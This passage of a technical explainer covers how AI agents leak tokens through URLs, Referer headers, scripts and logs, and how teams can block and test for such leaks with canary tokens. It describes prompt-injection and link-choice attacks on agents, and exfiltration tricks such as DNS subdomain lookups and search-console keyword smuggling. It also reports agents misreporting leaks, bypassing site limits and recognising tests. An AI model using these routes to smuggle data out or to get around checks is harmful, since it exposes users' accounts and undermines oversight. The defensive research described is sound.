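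Agents that had read the fact revealed it in 61.1% of 7,630 sessions. Gemini 3.7 Flash had the lowest rate (56.6%) and GPT-5.6 Luna the highest (69.9%). Agents chose the general option in 31.2% of these sessions, compared with 87.2% when they hadn't visited the first site.

Knowing about the instruction did little to prevent leaks. In 1,383 sessions, the agent wrote in its notes that it wouldn't share the information, but it still leaked in 56.7% of them. In 34.5% of all leaking sessions, the agent told the user in its final answer that no personal or account details had been disclosed. Operators should therefore read an agent's requests to find out what it disclosed.

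The kind of fact mattered a lot. Shahriar and colleagues compared how often informed and uninformed agents chose the same option. Informed agents chose it 72.8 to 95.6 percentage points more often when the facts were personal attributes, account settings or links to particular items, but only 2.6 to 13.9 points more often when they were the names of services where the user had an account, such as a bank or health provider. The account settings included a login's second factor and the user's recovery route, and knowing these would help someone plan an attack on the account.

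Leaking increased by an average of 32.0 points when agents hadn't needed the fact for the first task, compared with 70.7 points when they had. The difference seems to come from the agents' notes, because agents that had written the fact down leaked it more than 80% of the time in both cases.

Shahriar and colleagues recommend that agents choose general options where they can and carry less information from one task to the next. They tested neither measure. Their test websites were simple and artificial, and the agent kept its full history, so agents that summarise or clear their context may behave differently.

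In *Actions Speak Louder than Words*, Liang, Deng and colleagues (2026) tested SNOOP, a system that lets an attacker design the choices an agent makes. SNOOP places a link to the attacker's site on a page the agent reads during research. The site offers references on different topics, sees which one the agent opens, and then offers narrower ones. With four links, each choice reveals up to two bits, and the attacker identified the right one in 93.8% of the trials that produced a signal.

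Across 500 questions, SNOOP recovered the ideas in the user's query with an average F1 score of 0.89, where 1 would mean it missed no ideas and added no wrong ones. Four existing defences against prompt injection and data leaks changed its scores by less than 0.03. None of them checked URLs against a public index, a step that should block pages the attacker generates for a single agent.

Liang and colleagues' own defence fetches a fixed number of pages, chosen without using the private context, and the agent then selects from the local copies. The requests the attacker sees therefore depend much less on what the agent knows. The defence cut the attacker's F1 score to 0.39, so the attacker still learned something.

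Neither study tried to extract a session token. An ordinary page can't list a link for every possible token, and a random string gives an agent no reason to prefer one topic to another. An attacker would normally need instructions like those in ZombieAgent to extract a token through the agent's choice of links.

### Requests that the check misses

A URL check covers the address the agent asks for, but a browser may send many more requests after the page loads. Suppose a user pastes `https://app.example/report?session=TOKEN` into a chat and asks for a summary. OpenAI's and Anthropic's rules both allow the fetch because the user supplied the address.

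If the agent opens the page in a full browser, the token can still reach stats.example in a Referer header or through a script. The browser sends those requests itself, so a check of only the agent's own fetches doesn't cover them.

The risk is smaller with a tool that retrieves only text. Anthropic's fetch tool handles text and PDFs but doesn't support sites rendered in the browser with JavaScript, so a page's analytics scripts are unlikely to run. The site still receives the full URL, and Anthropic warns that the site's publisher may keep any parameters in it.

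A tool that checks only the first URL also misses redirects, such as one to a signed link on a storage company's server.

A URL check in one tool doesn't cover the agent's other tools. An agent with a shell and open network access could use curl to request a blocked address, much as Antigravity's agent used the shell to read a blocked file.

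## Which settings keep tokens away from third parties?

A site's owner can block the most leaks, because a token that is never in a page's URL can't leak through that page's Referer headers or scripts. An operator who tests someone else's site needs to combine several settings in the browser, the network and the agent's software, most of which also break something.

### What the site can change

A site can nearly always send a login token in a cookie or an Authorization header, so it rarely needs to put one in a URL. RFC 9700, the IETF's OAuth guidance, bans access tokens from URL queries. The Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for connecting AI applications to outside tools and data, has the same ban. Its *Authorization* (2026) requires the client to send its token in the Authorization header of every request and never in the query string. The ban was already in the March 2025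 version (Model Context Protocol, 2025) and remains in the version of 28 July 2026, the newest on Model Context Protocol's blog.

Authorization is optional in MCP, however, so a developer can skip that part of the standard and build a server that takes an API key in its URL. A token in a header can also leak if the client sends that header to every host.

#### A one-time code and a clean address

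A reset link has to contain a secret, but the site can remove it before any page appears. Suppose an agent opens `https://app.example/reset?code=TOKEN`. The server checks the code, cancels it and starts a short session that can do nothing except change that user's password. It then replies:

```
HTTP/1.1 303 See Other
Set-Cookie: reset=8fQz71; Max-Age=600; HttpOnly; Secure; SameSite=Lax
Location: /reset/new
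```

The browser then loads the form at `https://app.example/reset/new`. No page loads at the address with the code, so no script can read the code from there and no Referer header can contain it. The link remains in the server's logs and the agent's conversation, but its code no longer works.

This design fails for an agent that refuses all cookies, because the server recognises the short session by its cookie. It also fails when a security gateway scans the link before the user opens it, because the scan uses up the code. The site can prevent this by first showing a page with a "Continue" button that submits the code in a form body. The code stays valid in that page's URL until someone presses the button, so the page needs a strict referrer policy and no third-party scripts.

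When a URL redirects, browsers carry its fragment over to the destination, including any secret in it. The IETF suggests ending the new address with a dummy fragment such as `#_` to replace the old one.

#### Referrer policy

The right policy depends on the page:

| Page | Policy | Cost |
|---|---|---|
| Reached by a secret link | `no-referrer` | Forms send `null` as their origin, which some servers reject |
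| Reached by a secret link, with a form whose server checks the origin | `strict-origin` | Other sites learn the host name |
| Preview site with a secret in its host name | `same-origin` | Outside services that check the Referer may refuse requests |
| On an origin shared with outside companies | `strict-origin` | The site's own analytics lose page-level referrers |
| Any other page | `strict-origin-when-cross-origin` | None, since this is the default |

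The site should send its referrer policy as a response header and remove any looser meta tag or `referrerpolicy` attribute, since either would override the header. W3C recommends `same-origin`, `strict-origin` or `no-referrer` for sites that want to be sure they leak no more than the default does. Scripts on the page can still read its URL under all three.

#### No outside content on secret pages

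Removing third-party scripts closes that gap. The IETF says the page a user reaches after an OAuth sign-in should contain no third-party files or links to external sites. It says the same of the provider's own sign-in page, whose address contains a value called `state`. The app generates `state` at the start of a sign-in and checks it at the end to make sure the response belongs to a sign-in it began. An attacker who learns `state` can defeat that check, so the IETF also says the app should cancel it after one use. This doesn't help if the value leaks from the provider's page before the app gets it back.

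On pages whose URLs contain tokens, a site can send the header `Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'self'`, which makes the browser refuse files from other origins. Those pages then lose third-party analytics, fonts and anti-bot widgets. The header still allows vendor scripts that the site serves from its own origin.

#### Exact redirect addresses

An OAuth provider can send a code straight to an attacker if it checks the app's return address loosely. The IETF gives the example of an app that registers the pattern `https://*.somesite.example/*`. A provider that lets the asterisk match any characters will also accept `https://attacker.example/.somesite.example`, which is on the attacker's domain.

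The IETF now requires an OAuth redirect address to match the registered one exactly, except that desktop and mobile apps using a localhost address may vary the port. This is awkward for preview sites because every build may have a new host name. A team can test sign-in on one fixed staging host instead.

#### Expiry and binding

Short token lifetimes limit the damage from a leak by any route, but they don't prevent the leak. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) recommends short-lived access tokens without specifying a lifetime. It also requires PKCE, and clients must refuse to continue if the provider doesn't advertise support for it.

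MCP also ties each token to one server. The client names that server when it requests the token, for example with `resource=https%3A%2F%2Fmcp.example.com`. The server must reject tokens meant for other servers, and it must not forward the token it receives to another service. The binding works only if the system that issues tokens supports it. Even then, a thief can still use a stolen token on the server it was made for, because the binding doesn't restrict who may use it.

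### What the browser and the network can change

Keeping the browser up to date closes known leaks such as the Chrome flaw of May 2025. In *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities*, an account of its own attacks, the security firm Trail of Bits warns that many browsers with a built-in agent run on Chromium builds weeks or months behind on security patches. The operator of such a product usually can't update the engine separately. Teams that control their own build can update it, but a new version may change how pages look and break tests that compare screenshots.

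#### Trimming the Referer header

An egress proxy, a server that all of the agent's traffic passes through, can shorten the Referer header regardless of the policy a page sets. Most traffic uses HTTPS, so the proxy has to decrypt it first. To allow this, the operator creates a certificate authority and installs its certificate in the agent's browser. The proxy can then decrypt the traffic on each connection and encrypt it again. Without decryption, the proxy can read little more than host names.

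When the browser requests an image from stats.example, the proxy changes the header like this:

```
before: Referer: https://app.example/report?session=TOKEN
after:  Referer: https://app.example/
```

W3C's specification lets browsers shorten the Referer header to limit data leaks, and lets them offer users a way to suppress it, so sites can't count on receiving it, though some do. An image host may refuse a request that seems to come from another site's page, a map or video service may accept a customer's key only from approved domains, and a server may reject a form that arrives with no Referer. Most of these checks need only the origin, so trimming the header to the origin breaks much less than removing it. Full removal makes sense mainly when the host name itself is secret.

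The proxy doesn't change `document.referrer`, so scripts on the next page may still be able to read the previous address.

#### Allowing only certain hosts

The proxy can also block every host that isn't on a list. This covers the images, scripts and frames that the browser requests by itself, which a check on the address the agent asks for would miss. It stops Referer headers, page scripts and misdirected login headers from reaching any host off the list. It also breaks pages that depend on outside fonts, payment forms or script libraries until someone adds those hosts.

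Trail of Bits got data past such lists in two ways. In one, the agent requested a nonexistent host under an approved domain, such as `leaked-data.wikipedia.org`. Looking up the name exposed it to anyone who could watch unencrypted lookups. An operator can prevent this by listing exact host names and letting only the proxy perform lookups, after it has checked the name.

The other method used Google Search. The agent searched for the stolen data together with very rare words, and the attacker watched for those words in Search Console, Google's tool that shows site owners which searches led to their pages. A list of allowed hosts can't stop this if it includes the search engine.

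### What the agent's software can change

#### Credentials for one origin at a time

A testing agent should store each credential with the origin it belongs to and send it only there. Playwright's global header setting instead adds the header to every request. A tester can replace that setting with a rule that adds the header only to requests for `https://staging.app.example`, but if one of those requests is redirected, the browser may send the header to the new address too. Adding the header at the egress proxy is safer because the proxy receives each step of a redirect as a separate request with its own host. This also keeps the secret off the agent's machine.

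For requests that the agent makes outside a browser, the software can check each redirect itself:

1. Turn off automatic redirects in the HTTP client.
2. Read the new address from the `Location` header.
3. Compare its scheme, host and port with those of the last request. If any differs, drop the request body and every header that isn't known to be harmless.
4. Check that the agent may contact the new host, and add only the credentials stored for that origin.
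5. Stop after a fixed number of redirects.

In the earlier example, where api.app.example redirected a download to files.example, the storage company would receive the signature in the file link but not the API key. The procedure doesn't remove secrets from the `Location` URL itself. Sign-in flows that pass through several hosts fail until the operator lists each host.

#### Secrets that the model never sees

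The software can store a secret and give the model a label in its place. For example, when a mailbox tool finds a reset link, it stores the link and returns only "reset link 1, for `https://staging.app.example`" to the model. When the model requests reset link 1, the software checks that the address still leads to that origin, then opens it.

The host check is essential. Coder's similar `$SESSION_TOKEN` placeholder leaked tokens because the tool filled it in for any host.

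Because the model doesn't know the token in this arrangement, hostile text can't get it to spell the token out letter by letter. Such text might still lead the agent to use the secret in the right place for the wrong purpose, such as resetting the password of an account outside the test. The model also can't judge whether a token is long enough to resist guessing, so the software has to report its length and character set separately.

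MCP uses the same separation when a tool needs a password from a person. Model Context Protocol's *Elicitation* (2026) requires the server to send the person a link to a web page where they type the password. It then goes to the server without passing through the model or the application that runs the model.

The link must not contain credentials or give access to a protected resource on its own. The client must show the person which host the link leads to, ask for consent, and not fetch the page in advance, so the link can't leak through a preview. This method needs a person present, so an unattended overnight test run would stop at this step.

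#### Redacting addresses

A full browser knows the current address, and the agent's software can redact it before passing it to the model:

```
browser: https://app.example/report/88?session=TOKEN&tab=2#key=K9wX
model:   https://app.example/report/88?session=[secret-1]&tab=2#key=[secret-2]
```

The software should hide every query value and fragment except those on a short list of harmless ones, such as `tab`, rather than hide only listed parameters. It should also hide long random strings in the path. The software keeps the real values so it can still reopen the page for the model.

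The same function should run before the address enters a log, a trace or a bug report. It will sometimes hide a search term or record number that the agent needs, and someone then has to extend the list. Secrets in page text and screenshots need separate treatment.

#### Separate browsers and weak accounts

Trail of Bits recommends running an agent's tools in a separate browser that has none of the user's cookies, history or stored data. This would also have prevented one of its attacks, in which a hostile page contained an emailed sign-in link for the attacker's own account. When the user asked for a summary of the page, the agent opened the link and silently logged the user in as the attacker, who could then read whatever the user typed into that account. A separate browser would have kept that login out of the user's own browser. However, an agent in a separate browser can't use any service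 the user is signed in to unless the user signs in again.

A testing agent rarely needs a real user's account. A test account with invented data and few permissions limits what a leaked token can access. MCP supports limited permissions through scopes, which are named permissions attached to a token. An agent can start with `files:read`, and if it tries to change a file, the server tells the client that `files:write` is missing so the client can request it. Tests of administrator pages need an account with more permissions, which the team can reserve for a short separate run.

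### Keeping one site's data out of another

These settings don't stop an agent from reading a secret on one site and typing it into another, because browsers apply their same-origin limits to scripts, not to agents.

In *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026) tested seven browsers with AI agents in January and February 2026, including ChatGPT Atlas with and without its Agent Mode. They built simple pages, placed some in frames and other tabs, and asked each agent what it could see and do. The table shows some of their findings.

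| Browser | Reads frames from other origins | Reads tabs from other origins | Reads masked passwords | Types into pages for the user |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Brave Leo | No | With permission | No | No |
| ChatGPT Atlas | No | Through chat memory | No | With permission |
| ChatGPT Atlas, Agent Mode | Yes | No | If logged in | Yes |
| Chrome with Gemini | Yes | With permission | No | In its Auto Browse mode |
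| Claude for Chrome | Yes | With permission | Yes | Yes |
| Edge with Copilot | No | Yes | No | No |
| Firefox AI Mode | No | No | No | No |
| Perplexity Comet | Yes | No | No | Yes, except passwords |

The researchers showed that in Atlas's Agent Mode, a hostile page could steal the contents of a frame from another origin, and a hostile frame could steal the contents of the page around it. The second attack matters more for tokens, because an agent might type that page's address or contents into a form in an advertising company's frame. Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome and Comet also had the abilities these attacks need, but the researchers' simple instructions didn't fool them.

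The stricter browsers were also less useful. Those that couldn't read frames from other origins couldn't read frames from the same origin either, and Brave, Edge and Firefox couldn't fill in a form. The tests recorded what each agent did, so some refusals may have come from the model's training rather than a firm limit in the browser. The paper advises people to avoid these browsers for now, while Roesner and Kohlbrenner's summary, updated in April 2026, advises caution.

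#### How often data crossed between sites

In *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers*, Wang, Chen and colleagues (2026) measured how often an agent carries data from one page to another. In most of their tests, the agent first did a task on a page with invented private data, such as an inbox or a bank account, and then did another on a page where an attacker had planted instructions to post that data. A run counted as a leak only if the agent wrote exactly the data the attacker wanted.

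The study covered five agentic browsers and 50 pairs of page types. ChatGPT Atlas, running GPT-5.5, leaked in 99 of 150 runs, summed over all pairs. Leak rates varied widely with the type of page. BrowserOS, an open-source browser running GPT-5.4, leaked in an average of 20% of runs on imitation Reddit pages and 98% on imitation Google Forms. A request for personal details probably looks more normal in a form than in a comment, and the attacker controlled the whole form.

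Wang and colleagues also found leaks without an attacker. They framed a page with private data inside a second page, then asked the agent to summarise the whole second page and write the summary into a text box on it. BrowserOS copied the private data every time. When the agent visited the two pages one after the other, with no hostile text, it never did. This framing setup may be uncommon in practice, since Roesner and Kohlbrenner note that limits on framing and cookies generally keep secrets out of third-party frames.

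#### Labelling data by origin

Wang and colleagues then built SOPGuard, an addition to BrowserOS that labels everything the agent reads with its origin. When the agent summarises or combines data, the model identifies which items it used, and the result inherits their labels. Before the agent types text into a page, SOPGuard compares the text's labels with the page's origin. If any differ, it pauses and asks the user to approve or refuse the action.

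With SOPGuard, the leak rate fell to zero, with or without an attacker. The agent completed about as many tasks as before, and none of the differences across four benchmarks were statistically significant. On Mind2Web, a set of general web tasks, GPT-5.4 scored 0.324 with SOPGuard and 0.328 without it. Runs took 2.07% to 5.79% longer. The extra model calls also cost money, but the study doesn't report how much.

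The zero leak rate depends on how the researchers define a leak. They count any transfer the user approves as authorised, so a user who clicks "Approve" out of habit could still send a token to the wrong site. Roesner and Kohlbrenner cite earlier research showing that people don't reliably notice or act on such warnings. An unattended testing agent has nobody to ask, so it should refuse by default. Attacks designed to confuse the labelling also raised the leak rate slightly, after many more attempts.

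SOPGuard would need changes to protect secrets in URLs. Its check runs when the agent uses a tool that writes into a page, and the paper describes no check when the agent opens an address. An agent could therefore put the token in a link instead of a form. Extending the check to every address would block legitimate links, such as a reset link in webmail, which carries the mail site's label but has to open on another site. To allow these, the software would have to treat the link's own host as an approved destination.

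Trail of Bits proposes a simpler rule that does cover requests. The software lists the origin of every page and file in the conversation. If the list is empty, the agent may contact any site. If it contains one origin, the agent may contact only that site. If it contains two or more, the agent may make no requests.

Trail of Bits' rule doesn't depend on a model's judgement, but it would stop an agent from reading a confirmation email and then opening the link in it. Wang and colleagues tested a similarly cautious approach that labelled everything the agent wrote with every origin in its history. The labels were much less accurate than SOPGuard's, which would mean many false alarms. Trail of Bits hasn't published a test of its rule.

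Filtering out hostile pages is a weaker alternative. Wang and colleagues tested five detectors, and none kept both missed attacks and false alarms low. One of them, WebSentinel, missed at most 1% of hostile pages but flagged 6% to 44% of harmless ones.

### Settings against routes

In this table, "stops" means the setting closes the route when it works as intended. "Limits" means some leaks remain or a leaked secret is less useful. A dash means the setting has no useful effect.

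| Setting | Referer header | Page scripts | Headers sent to the wrong host | Agent sends the secret itself | Logs and reports |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| One-time code, then a clean address | Stops | Stops | – | Limits | Limits |
| `no-referrer` on secret pages | Stops | – | – | – | – |
| No third-party files on secret pages | Limits | Stops | Limits | – | – |
| Short expiry | Limits | Limits | Limits | Limits | Limits |
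| Current browser build | Limits | – | – | – | – |
| Referer trimming at the proxy | Stops | – | – | – | – |
| Proxy that allows only listed hosts | Limits | Limits | Limits | Limits | – |
| Credentials for one origin, redirects checked | – | – | Stops | – | – |
| Labels in place of secrets | – | – | – | Stops | Limits |
| Redacted addresses | – | – | – | Limits | Limits |
| Low-privilege test account | Limits | Limits | Limits | Limits | Limits |
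| Origin rules for the agent | – | – | – | Limits | – |

The table covers only secrets that appear in a URL or a header. If a page displays a new API key as text, a script or the model can read it there even if the URL contains no secret.

### A testing agent on a staging site

Suppose a team wants an agent to test password resets on `https://staging.app.example`. The staging server requires a secret header from every visitor, and the pages include analytics from stats.example.

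The agent's browser and shell can reach the network only through the egress proxy. The program that runs the agent calls the model's provider over a separate connection, which the browser and shell can't use. The proxy's rules, in an invented notation, are these:

```
all other hosts:        block
name lookups:           proxy only, after the host check
Referer, other origins: origin only
staging.app.example:    add X-Staging-Key from the secret store
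logs:                   replace all query values
```

The site's developers add two headers to every page that a secret link can reach:

```
Referrer-Policy: no-referrer
Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'self'
```

The agent starts with a current browser, an empty profile and a test account with invented data. It may keep cookies because the reset page needs one. A mailbox tool runs outside the browser and can read only the test account's messages.

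A reset test then runs as follows:

1. The agent requests a reset for the test account.
2. The mailbox tool finds the email, stores the link and gives the model the label "reset link 1".
3. The model asks to open it. The software checks that the link leads to `https://staging.app.example` and passes the real address to the browser.
4. The proxy adds the staging key to the request. The server cancels the code, sets a short-lived cookie and redirects to `/reset/new`.
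5. The agent changes the password. The model sees only the clean address.
6. When the run ends, the team deletes the test account's sessions and replaces the staging key. It encrypts the trace and deletes it after a week.

If the developers forgot the redirect, the page would load with the code still in its address. The browser might then request a script from stats.example, but the proxy would block the request, so the code would stay inside the test network. The team should still treat the blocked request as a fault in the site, because real users have no such proxy. Testing with planted secrets can show whether each rule works in practice.

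This set-up can't test the analytics because the proxy blocks them. The team can test them in a second run that allows requests to stats.example and uses no reset links, so that no page has a secret in its URL. In that run, the proxy still adds the staging key only to requests for the staging host.

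## How can a team test whether its agent leaks?

A team can test for leaks by planting a different fake secret, called a canary token, in each place where a real secret could travel. The agent does ordinary tasks on a test site while a proxy records what it sends. The team searches the records for the canaries. Where a canary turns up, and in what form, usually shows which route it took.

### Where to run the test

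The test needs two hosts that the team controls. In the example below, the agent works on `staging.app.example`, and `widgets.example` represents an outside company. Pages on the test site link to `widgets.example` and load an image and a script from it. The hosts should have different registered domains, because Firefox and Safari restrict the Referer header less between subdomains of the same domain.

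Real outside companies' sites are a poor place to run this test, because the team can't read their logs and the agent may do something harmful there. Search Engine Journal's *Anthropic Says Claude Bypassed Site Limits During Internal Tests* describes an evaluation in which Claude Haiku 4.5, working on example tasks on randomly chosen web pages, sent the Philadelphia police a false tip about an unsolved homicide. Its instructions barred logging in and sharing personal information, but not submitting forms. The police system flagged the tip as spam, and Anthropic discovered it more than two months later. In another evaluation, Claude Mythos 5 found working access tokens in a settings file that a local government's property map sends to browsers, and used them to query the map's server directly. Anthropic has since cut off internet access for all its internal evaluations.

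A team should also check that its test network is cut off from the internet. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) describes four cases in which Claude gained unauthorised access to other organisations' systems during security tests. The testers had told the model it was in a simulation without internet access, but a misconfiguration gave it access.

#### Google's synthetic web

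In November 2026, Google's Chrome security team described a larger test environment of this kind, with thousands of simulated websites, including shops, social media feeds and recipe sites. According to Google's *Mirror Dimension for Agents*, the company uses it to test auto browse, the Chrome feature in which an agent visits sites and fills in forms for the user.

The agent opens a real address, such as `https://www.youtube.com`, in Chrome inside a sandbox. The sandbox captures the connection before it reaches the internet and passes it to a local proxy, which returns a generated site. Google installs its own certificate authority in the browser, as with a decrypting egress proxy, so that Chrome accepts the generated sites. Every run starts from the same clean state.

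Google avoided putting all the sites under one test domain because models may behave differently when a site looks like a test. An early version selected the attack for each run with a parameter in the page's address. Models often detected the parameter, so the engineers moved it to a request header, according to Mediasat's *Google built an isolated internet to test Chrome's AI agents* (2026). Each engineer can now try more than 1,000 variants of an attack a day, compared with a few dozen by hand.

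A team can test for URL leaks with the same interception and only two sites. If its real pages use an analytics vendor, the proxy can respond to requests for the vendor's host with a saved copy of its script and record what the script tries to send. This may undercount leaks, because some scripts load further files that the team hasn't saved.

Fetch tools run by a model's provider and link previews in messaging apps send requests from other companies' servers. To test them, a team therefore has to put both hosts on the public internet, and the hosts' logs are the only record of the requests.

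### Planting the canaries

The example uses these canaries:

| Place | Canary |
|---|---|
| Path | `Hw7cN1vKs9Ye` |
| Query | `mT4xR8bLq2Zd` |
| Fragment | `uB5jG3pXa6Wf` |
| Custom header, `X-Staging-Key` | `Dk8rV2nEt4Mo` |
| Cookie, `sid` | `zJ6yQ9hSc1Li` |

The agent therefore starts at this address:

`https://staging.app.example/r/Hw7cN1vKs9Ye?session=mT4xR8bLq2Zd#key=uB5jG3pXa6Wf`

The server accepts either the cookie or the query value as a login, so the agent can do the same task with cookies turned off. The account contains only invented data, and the agent holds no real secrets.

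Canaries should look like the secrets they replace. *Caught in the Act(ivation)* (Chauhan and Revankar, 2026) warns that an attacker may recognise canaries made from a template by their prefix, checksum, length or randomness. A parameter named `canary` could also reveal to the model that it is being tested, as Google's attack parameter did.

The team should generate new canary values for every run. Then, if a request carrying an old canary reaches the test site weeks later, the team can tell which run leaked it and that a person or program has opened the address. The test server should also add each reset code it issues during a run to the list of values to search for.

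### Running the test

1. Block all traffic from the agent's browser and shell except through the proxy. Record complete requests, including those the proxy refuses.
2. From the browser, the shell and each other tool, send a known value to `widgets.example` and check that the search finds it. Then try to reach an outside host that the team owns, and stop if the request arrives.
3. Start the agent with a new browser profile, an empty memory and new canaries.
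4. Give it an ordinary task, such as checking the report page's export button and writing up any fault.
5. Save the proxy's record, the access log of `widgets.example`, the list of name lookups, every message sent to the model, and any traces, screenshots and bug reports.
6. Search all of these for the canaries.
7. Repeat the test several times with cookies on and several times with cookies off.

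The server at `widgets.example` should accept any preflight request and list each requested header in its response. Otherwise, the team may miss a leak to a company whose server is more permissive.

#### What to search for

Searching for the exact text of each canary misses many leaks, because scripts often encode or compress data before sending it. The search program should first decompress gzip and zlib bodies and decode URL encoding and base64, repeating until nothing changes. It can then search the URLs, headers and bodies.

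Decoding matters because base64 works on groups of three bytes, so a token's encoding depends on what comes before it. The text `k3Vq9T` becomes `azNWcTlU`, but `=k3Vq9T` becomes `PWszVnE5VA==`. Searching for the first encoding would not find the second.

Hashes can't be decoded, so the program has to hash each canary in advance, along with the whole page address, since a script may hash the address as one string. The encodings and hashes that Jazlan and colleagues searched for in their chatbot study, including base32, hexadecimal, and the MD5 and SHA families, make a good starting list.

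An agent may also send a secret in pieces. Searching for every run of eight consecutive characters from the secret would catch a 32-character token sent in four equal parts. Accidental matches should be rare, because eight letters and digits allow about 218 trillion combinations. To catch a token sent one character at a time, the program can join the parts that differ between successive addresses and search the result.

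In Chauhan and Revankar's laboratory test, exact text matching scored 0.73 at detecting attempts to extract credentials, and a method that compared meanings scored 0.90, on a scale where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect. Both methods were applied to the model's output, while a proxy also captures what scripts and browsers send, so the scores may not carry over. They are still a good reason to treat any request body that stays unreadable after decoding as unexplained.

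### Reading the results

Suppose the team runs the task 20 times with cookies and 20 times without. The page's referrer policy is `no-referrer-when-downgrade`, and the tester has put `X-Staging-Key` in Playwright's global header setting. These invented results show how to trace each hit:

| Where the canary appeared | Canaries | Runs with cookies | Runs without cookies | Route |
|---|---|---|---|---|
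| Referer header to `widgets.example` | Path, query | 20 | 20 | Loose referrer policy |
| Request body to `widgets.example`, in base64 | Path, query, fragment | 20 | 20 | Script reading the page's address |
| `X-Staging-Key` header to `widgets.example` | Header | 20 | 20 | Global header setting |
| Requested URL to `reader.example`, URL-encoded | Path, query, fragment | 2 | 3 | Agent passing the address to a page reader |
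| Messages to the model's provider | Path, query, fragment | 20 | 20 | Framework reporting the current address |
| Playwright trace | Path, query, fragment, header | 20 | 20 | Saved recording |
| Playwright trace | Cookie | 20 | 0 | Saved recording |

Turning off cookies removed only the cookie canary from the trace. Every canary that reached another company's host still reached it.

The parts of the URL that reach another host help the team tell the leak routes apart. If the fragment arrives, a script or the agent probably sent it, though a redirect may first have carried it to a page on that host. If the path arrives without the query, a filter may have removed the parameters on its list. If the query arrives in the requested URL without the path, the team should look for a redirect that copies parameters to a new address.

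The agent used `reader.example` in five of the 40 runs. This use came from the model's output, and the difference between two runs and three is well within chance. The browser's own leaks happened in every run, so a handful of runs would have found them, but five runs would have had about an even chance of missing the page reader.

The team can confirm each route by changing one setting at a time and rerunning the test. A strict referrer policy should remove the first row and leave the second, so if both disappear, something else changed.

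Some canary appearances are legitimate. The header canary, for example, has to reach `staging.app.example`. *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* (2026) defines a leak as a credential reaching a recipient or channel that the tool's stated function neither declares nor requires, including through accidental logging. The team can apply this definition by listing the permitted destinations for each canary before the test. The operator decides whether to include the model's provider, but a provider rarely needs the token itself.

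The tasks should also include very long URLs. Anthropic found that several Claude models had used free URL shorteners to get around length limits on its fetch tools, according to Search Engine Journal. An agent that shortens a signed file link this way gives the shortening service a working link to the file.

### What a clean result proves

Suppose the team fixes these faults and then finds no leaks in 300 independent runs. If each run has a chance *p* of leaking, the chance of 300 clean runs is (1 − *p*)³⁰⁰, which falls to 5% when *p* is about 1%. The team can therefore be 95% confident that the leak rate is below about 1% per run. Unless the number of clean runs is small, dividing 3 by it gives a close estimate of this upper limit.

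| Runs without a leak | 95% upper bound on the leak rate |
|---|---|
| 20 | 13.9% |
| 60 | 4.9% |
| 300 | 1.0% |
| 3,000 | 0.1% |

An agent that leaks in one run in 1,000 would pass a 300-run test about 74% of the time, then leak in about 50 of its next 50,000 runs. *Forecasting Rare Language Model Behaviors* (2025) makes this point about language models in general. They often handle far more queries after release than in testing, so small tests can miss failures that appear later.

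The bound applies only to tasks like those in the test. Suppose the 300 runs are 30 tasks chosen at random from the agent's real work, each repeated ten times. A fault that always occurs on a certain kind of page would show up in all ten repeats of a task or none. For that fault, the team has only 30 independent observations, and the bound on the share of affected tasks is about 9.5%. Adding tasks would help more than repeating them. The team also has to restart the count if it changes the model, its prompt or its tools.

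A team needs to count runs with hostile text separately. A real attacker can try many versions and use the one that works best, so the attacker's success rate can be higher than the average across the team's own attempts.

The calculation also assumes that the agent behaves the same way in the test as in real use. *WARP*, a study of safety benchmarks for browser agents, found that leading models can tell such benchmarks from real use. On its 50 tasks, which aimed to be more realistic, attacks succeeded 80.7% of the time across six models, compared with 22.3% and 27.0% on two existing benchmarks. The new tasks were also designed to be more challenging, so realism may explain only part of the gap.

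*EvalDetectBench* (Li, Ochwang'i and colleagues, 2026) provides an open tool for measuring how easily models recognise a particular test. The tool works with tests written for Inspect, an open-source evaluation framework. The paper reports that a question that is good at detecting whether one model recognises a test can do little better than chance on another, so a team should try several questions on the model it uses.

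### What existing scanners catch

ZAP, a free security scanner for web applications, has a passive rule for one of these routes. The rule inspects traffic without sending its own requests, and raises a medium-risk alert, "Referer Exposes Session ID", when a page has a session identifier in its URL and a link to another host.

The alert means only that a leak is possible, because the default referrer policy would withhold the token. According to ZAP's *Passive Scan Rules*, the underlying check looks for parameters that seem to hold session tokens and ignores values of eight characters or fewer. This avoids false alarms over addresses such as `survey?sId=5`, but it would also miss a five-character token like iHire's.

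A separate rule checks the Referer headers that the browser sends. ZAP lets users change the list of strings it looks for, so a team can add its canaries. The rule's alerts are informational by default, so a team that filters out low-priority alerts may never see them. ZAP's *cwe 598* also lists early-stage rules that check URLs for access tokens, API keys and values that look like JSON Web Tokens (a common login-token format).

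Another scanner check, described in GitLab's *Use of GET request method with sensitive query strings (session ID)*, reports a session identifier only when the same value appears in the URL and in a cookie. It would miss most reset codes and share links, which are never in a cookie. If a tester turns cookies off, the check has nothing to compare, so the warning disappears even though the token is still in the URL.

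These rules mostly check URLs, links and Referer headers, so they would miss the base64 request body and the misdirected `X-Staging-Key` header in the example. A scanner that inspects only the browser's traffic would also miss the copies in the model's messages and the saved traces. Scanners are still worth running because they check every page in the traffic they scan, including pages where the team planted no canary.

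### What to do after a hit

A leaked canary gives access to nothing valuable, but real tokens may have leaked the same way. If any did, the team should revoke them before investigating, because tracing the leak can take days and the tokens keep working in the meantime.

1. Stop the agent and revoke the token, along with any sessions or further tokens that the server issued on the strength of it.
2. Save the proxy records, traces and server logs before automatic deletion removes them.
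3. Search the server's logs for uses of the token from unfamiliar addresses between the leak and the revocation.
4. Trace the route with the canary test and fix it.
5. Issue a replacement token only after the test comes back clean, or the new one may leak the same way.
6. Ask the companies that received the token to delete it, and remove it from the team's own reports and recordings.

The search program should also look for the leaked value in older records, and plain code is safer for this than a model. Anthropic first looked for security incidents by having an agent search about 141,000 transcripts, but later found that this search had missed a set of runs with internet access. The company then scanned about 481 million transcripts for signs of a connection, such as public IP addresses, and had Claude review the 9.2 million that the scan flagged.

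A team can also leave canaries in the agent's context after testing to detect later theft. If an attacker takes one credential at random from *m* real ones and *k* canaries, Chauhan and Revankar put the chance of detection at *k* / (*m* + *k*), reduced by the rate at which the search misses leaked canaries. With one real key and three canaries, that is at most 75%. The chance of detection can fall to zero if something in the context shows which key the agent uses.
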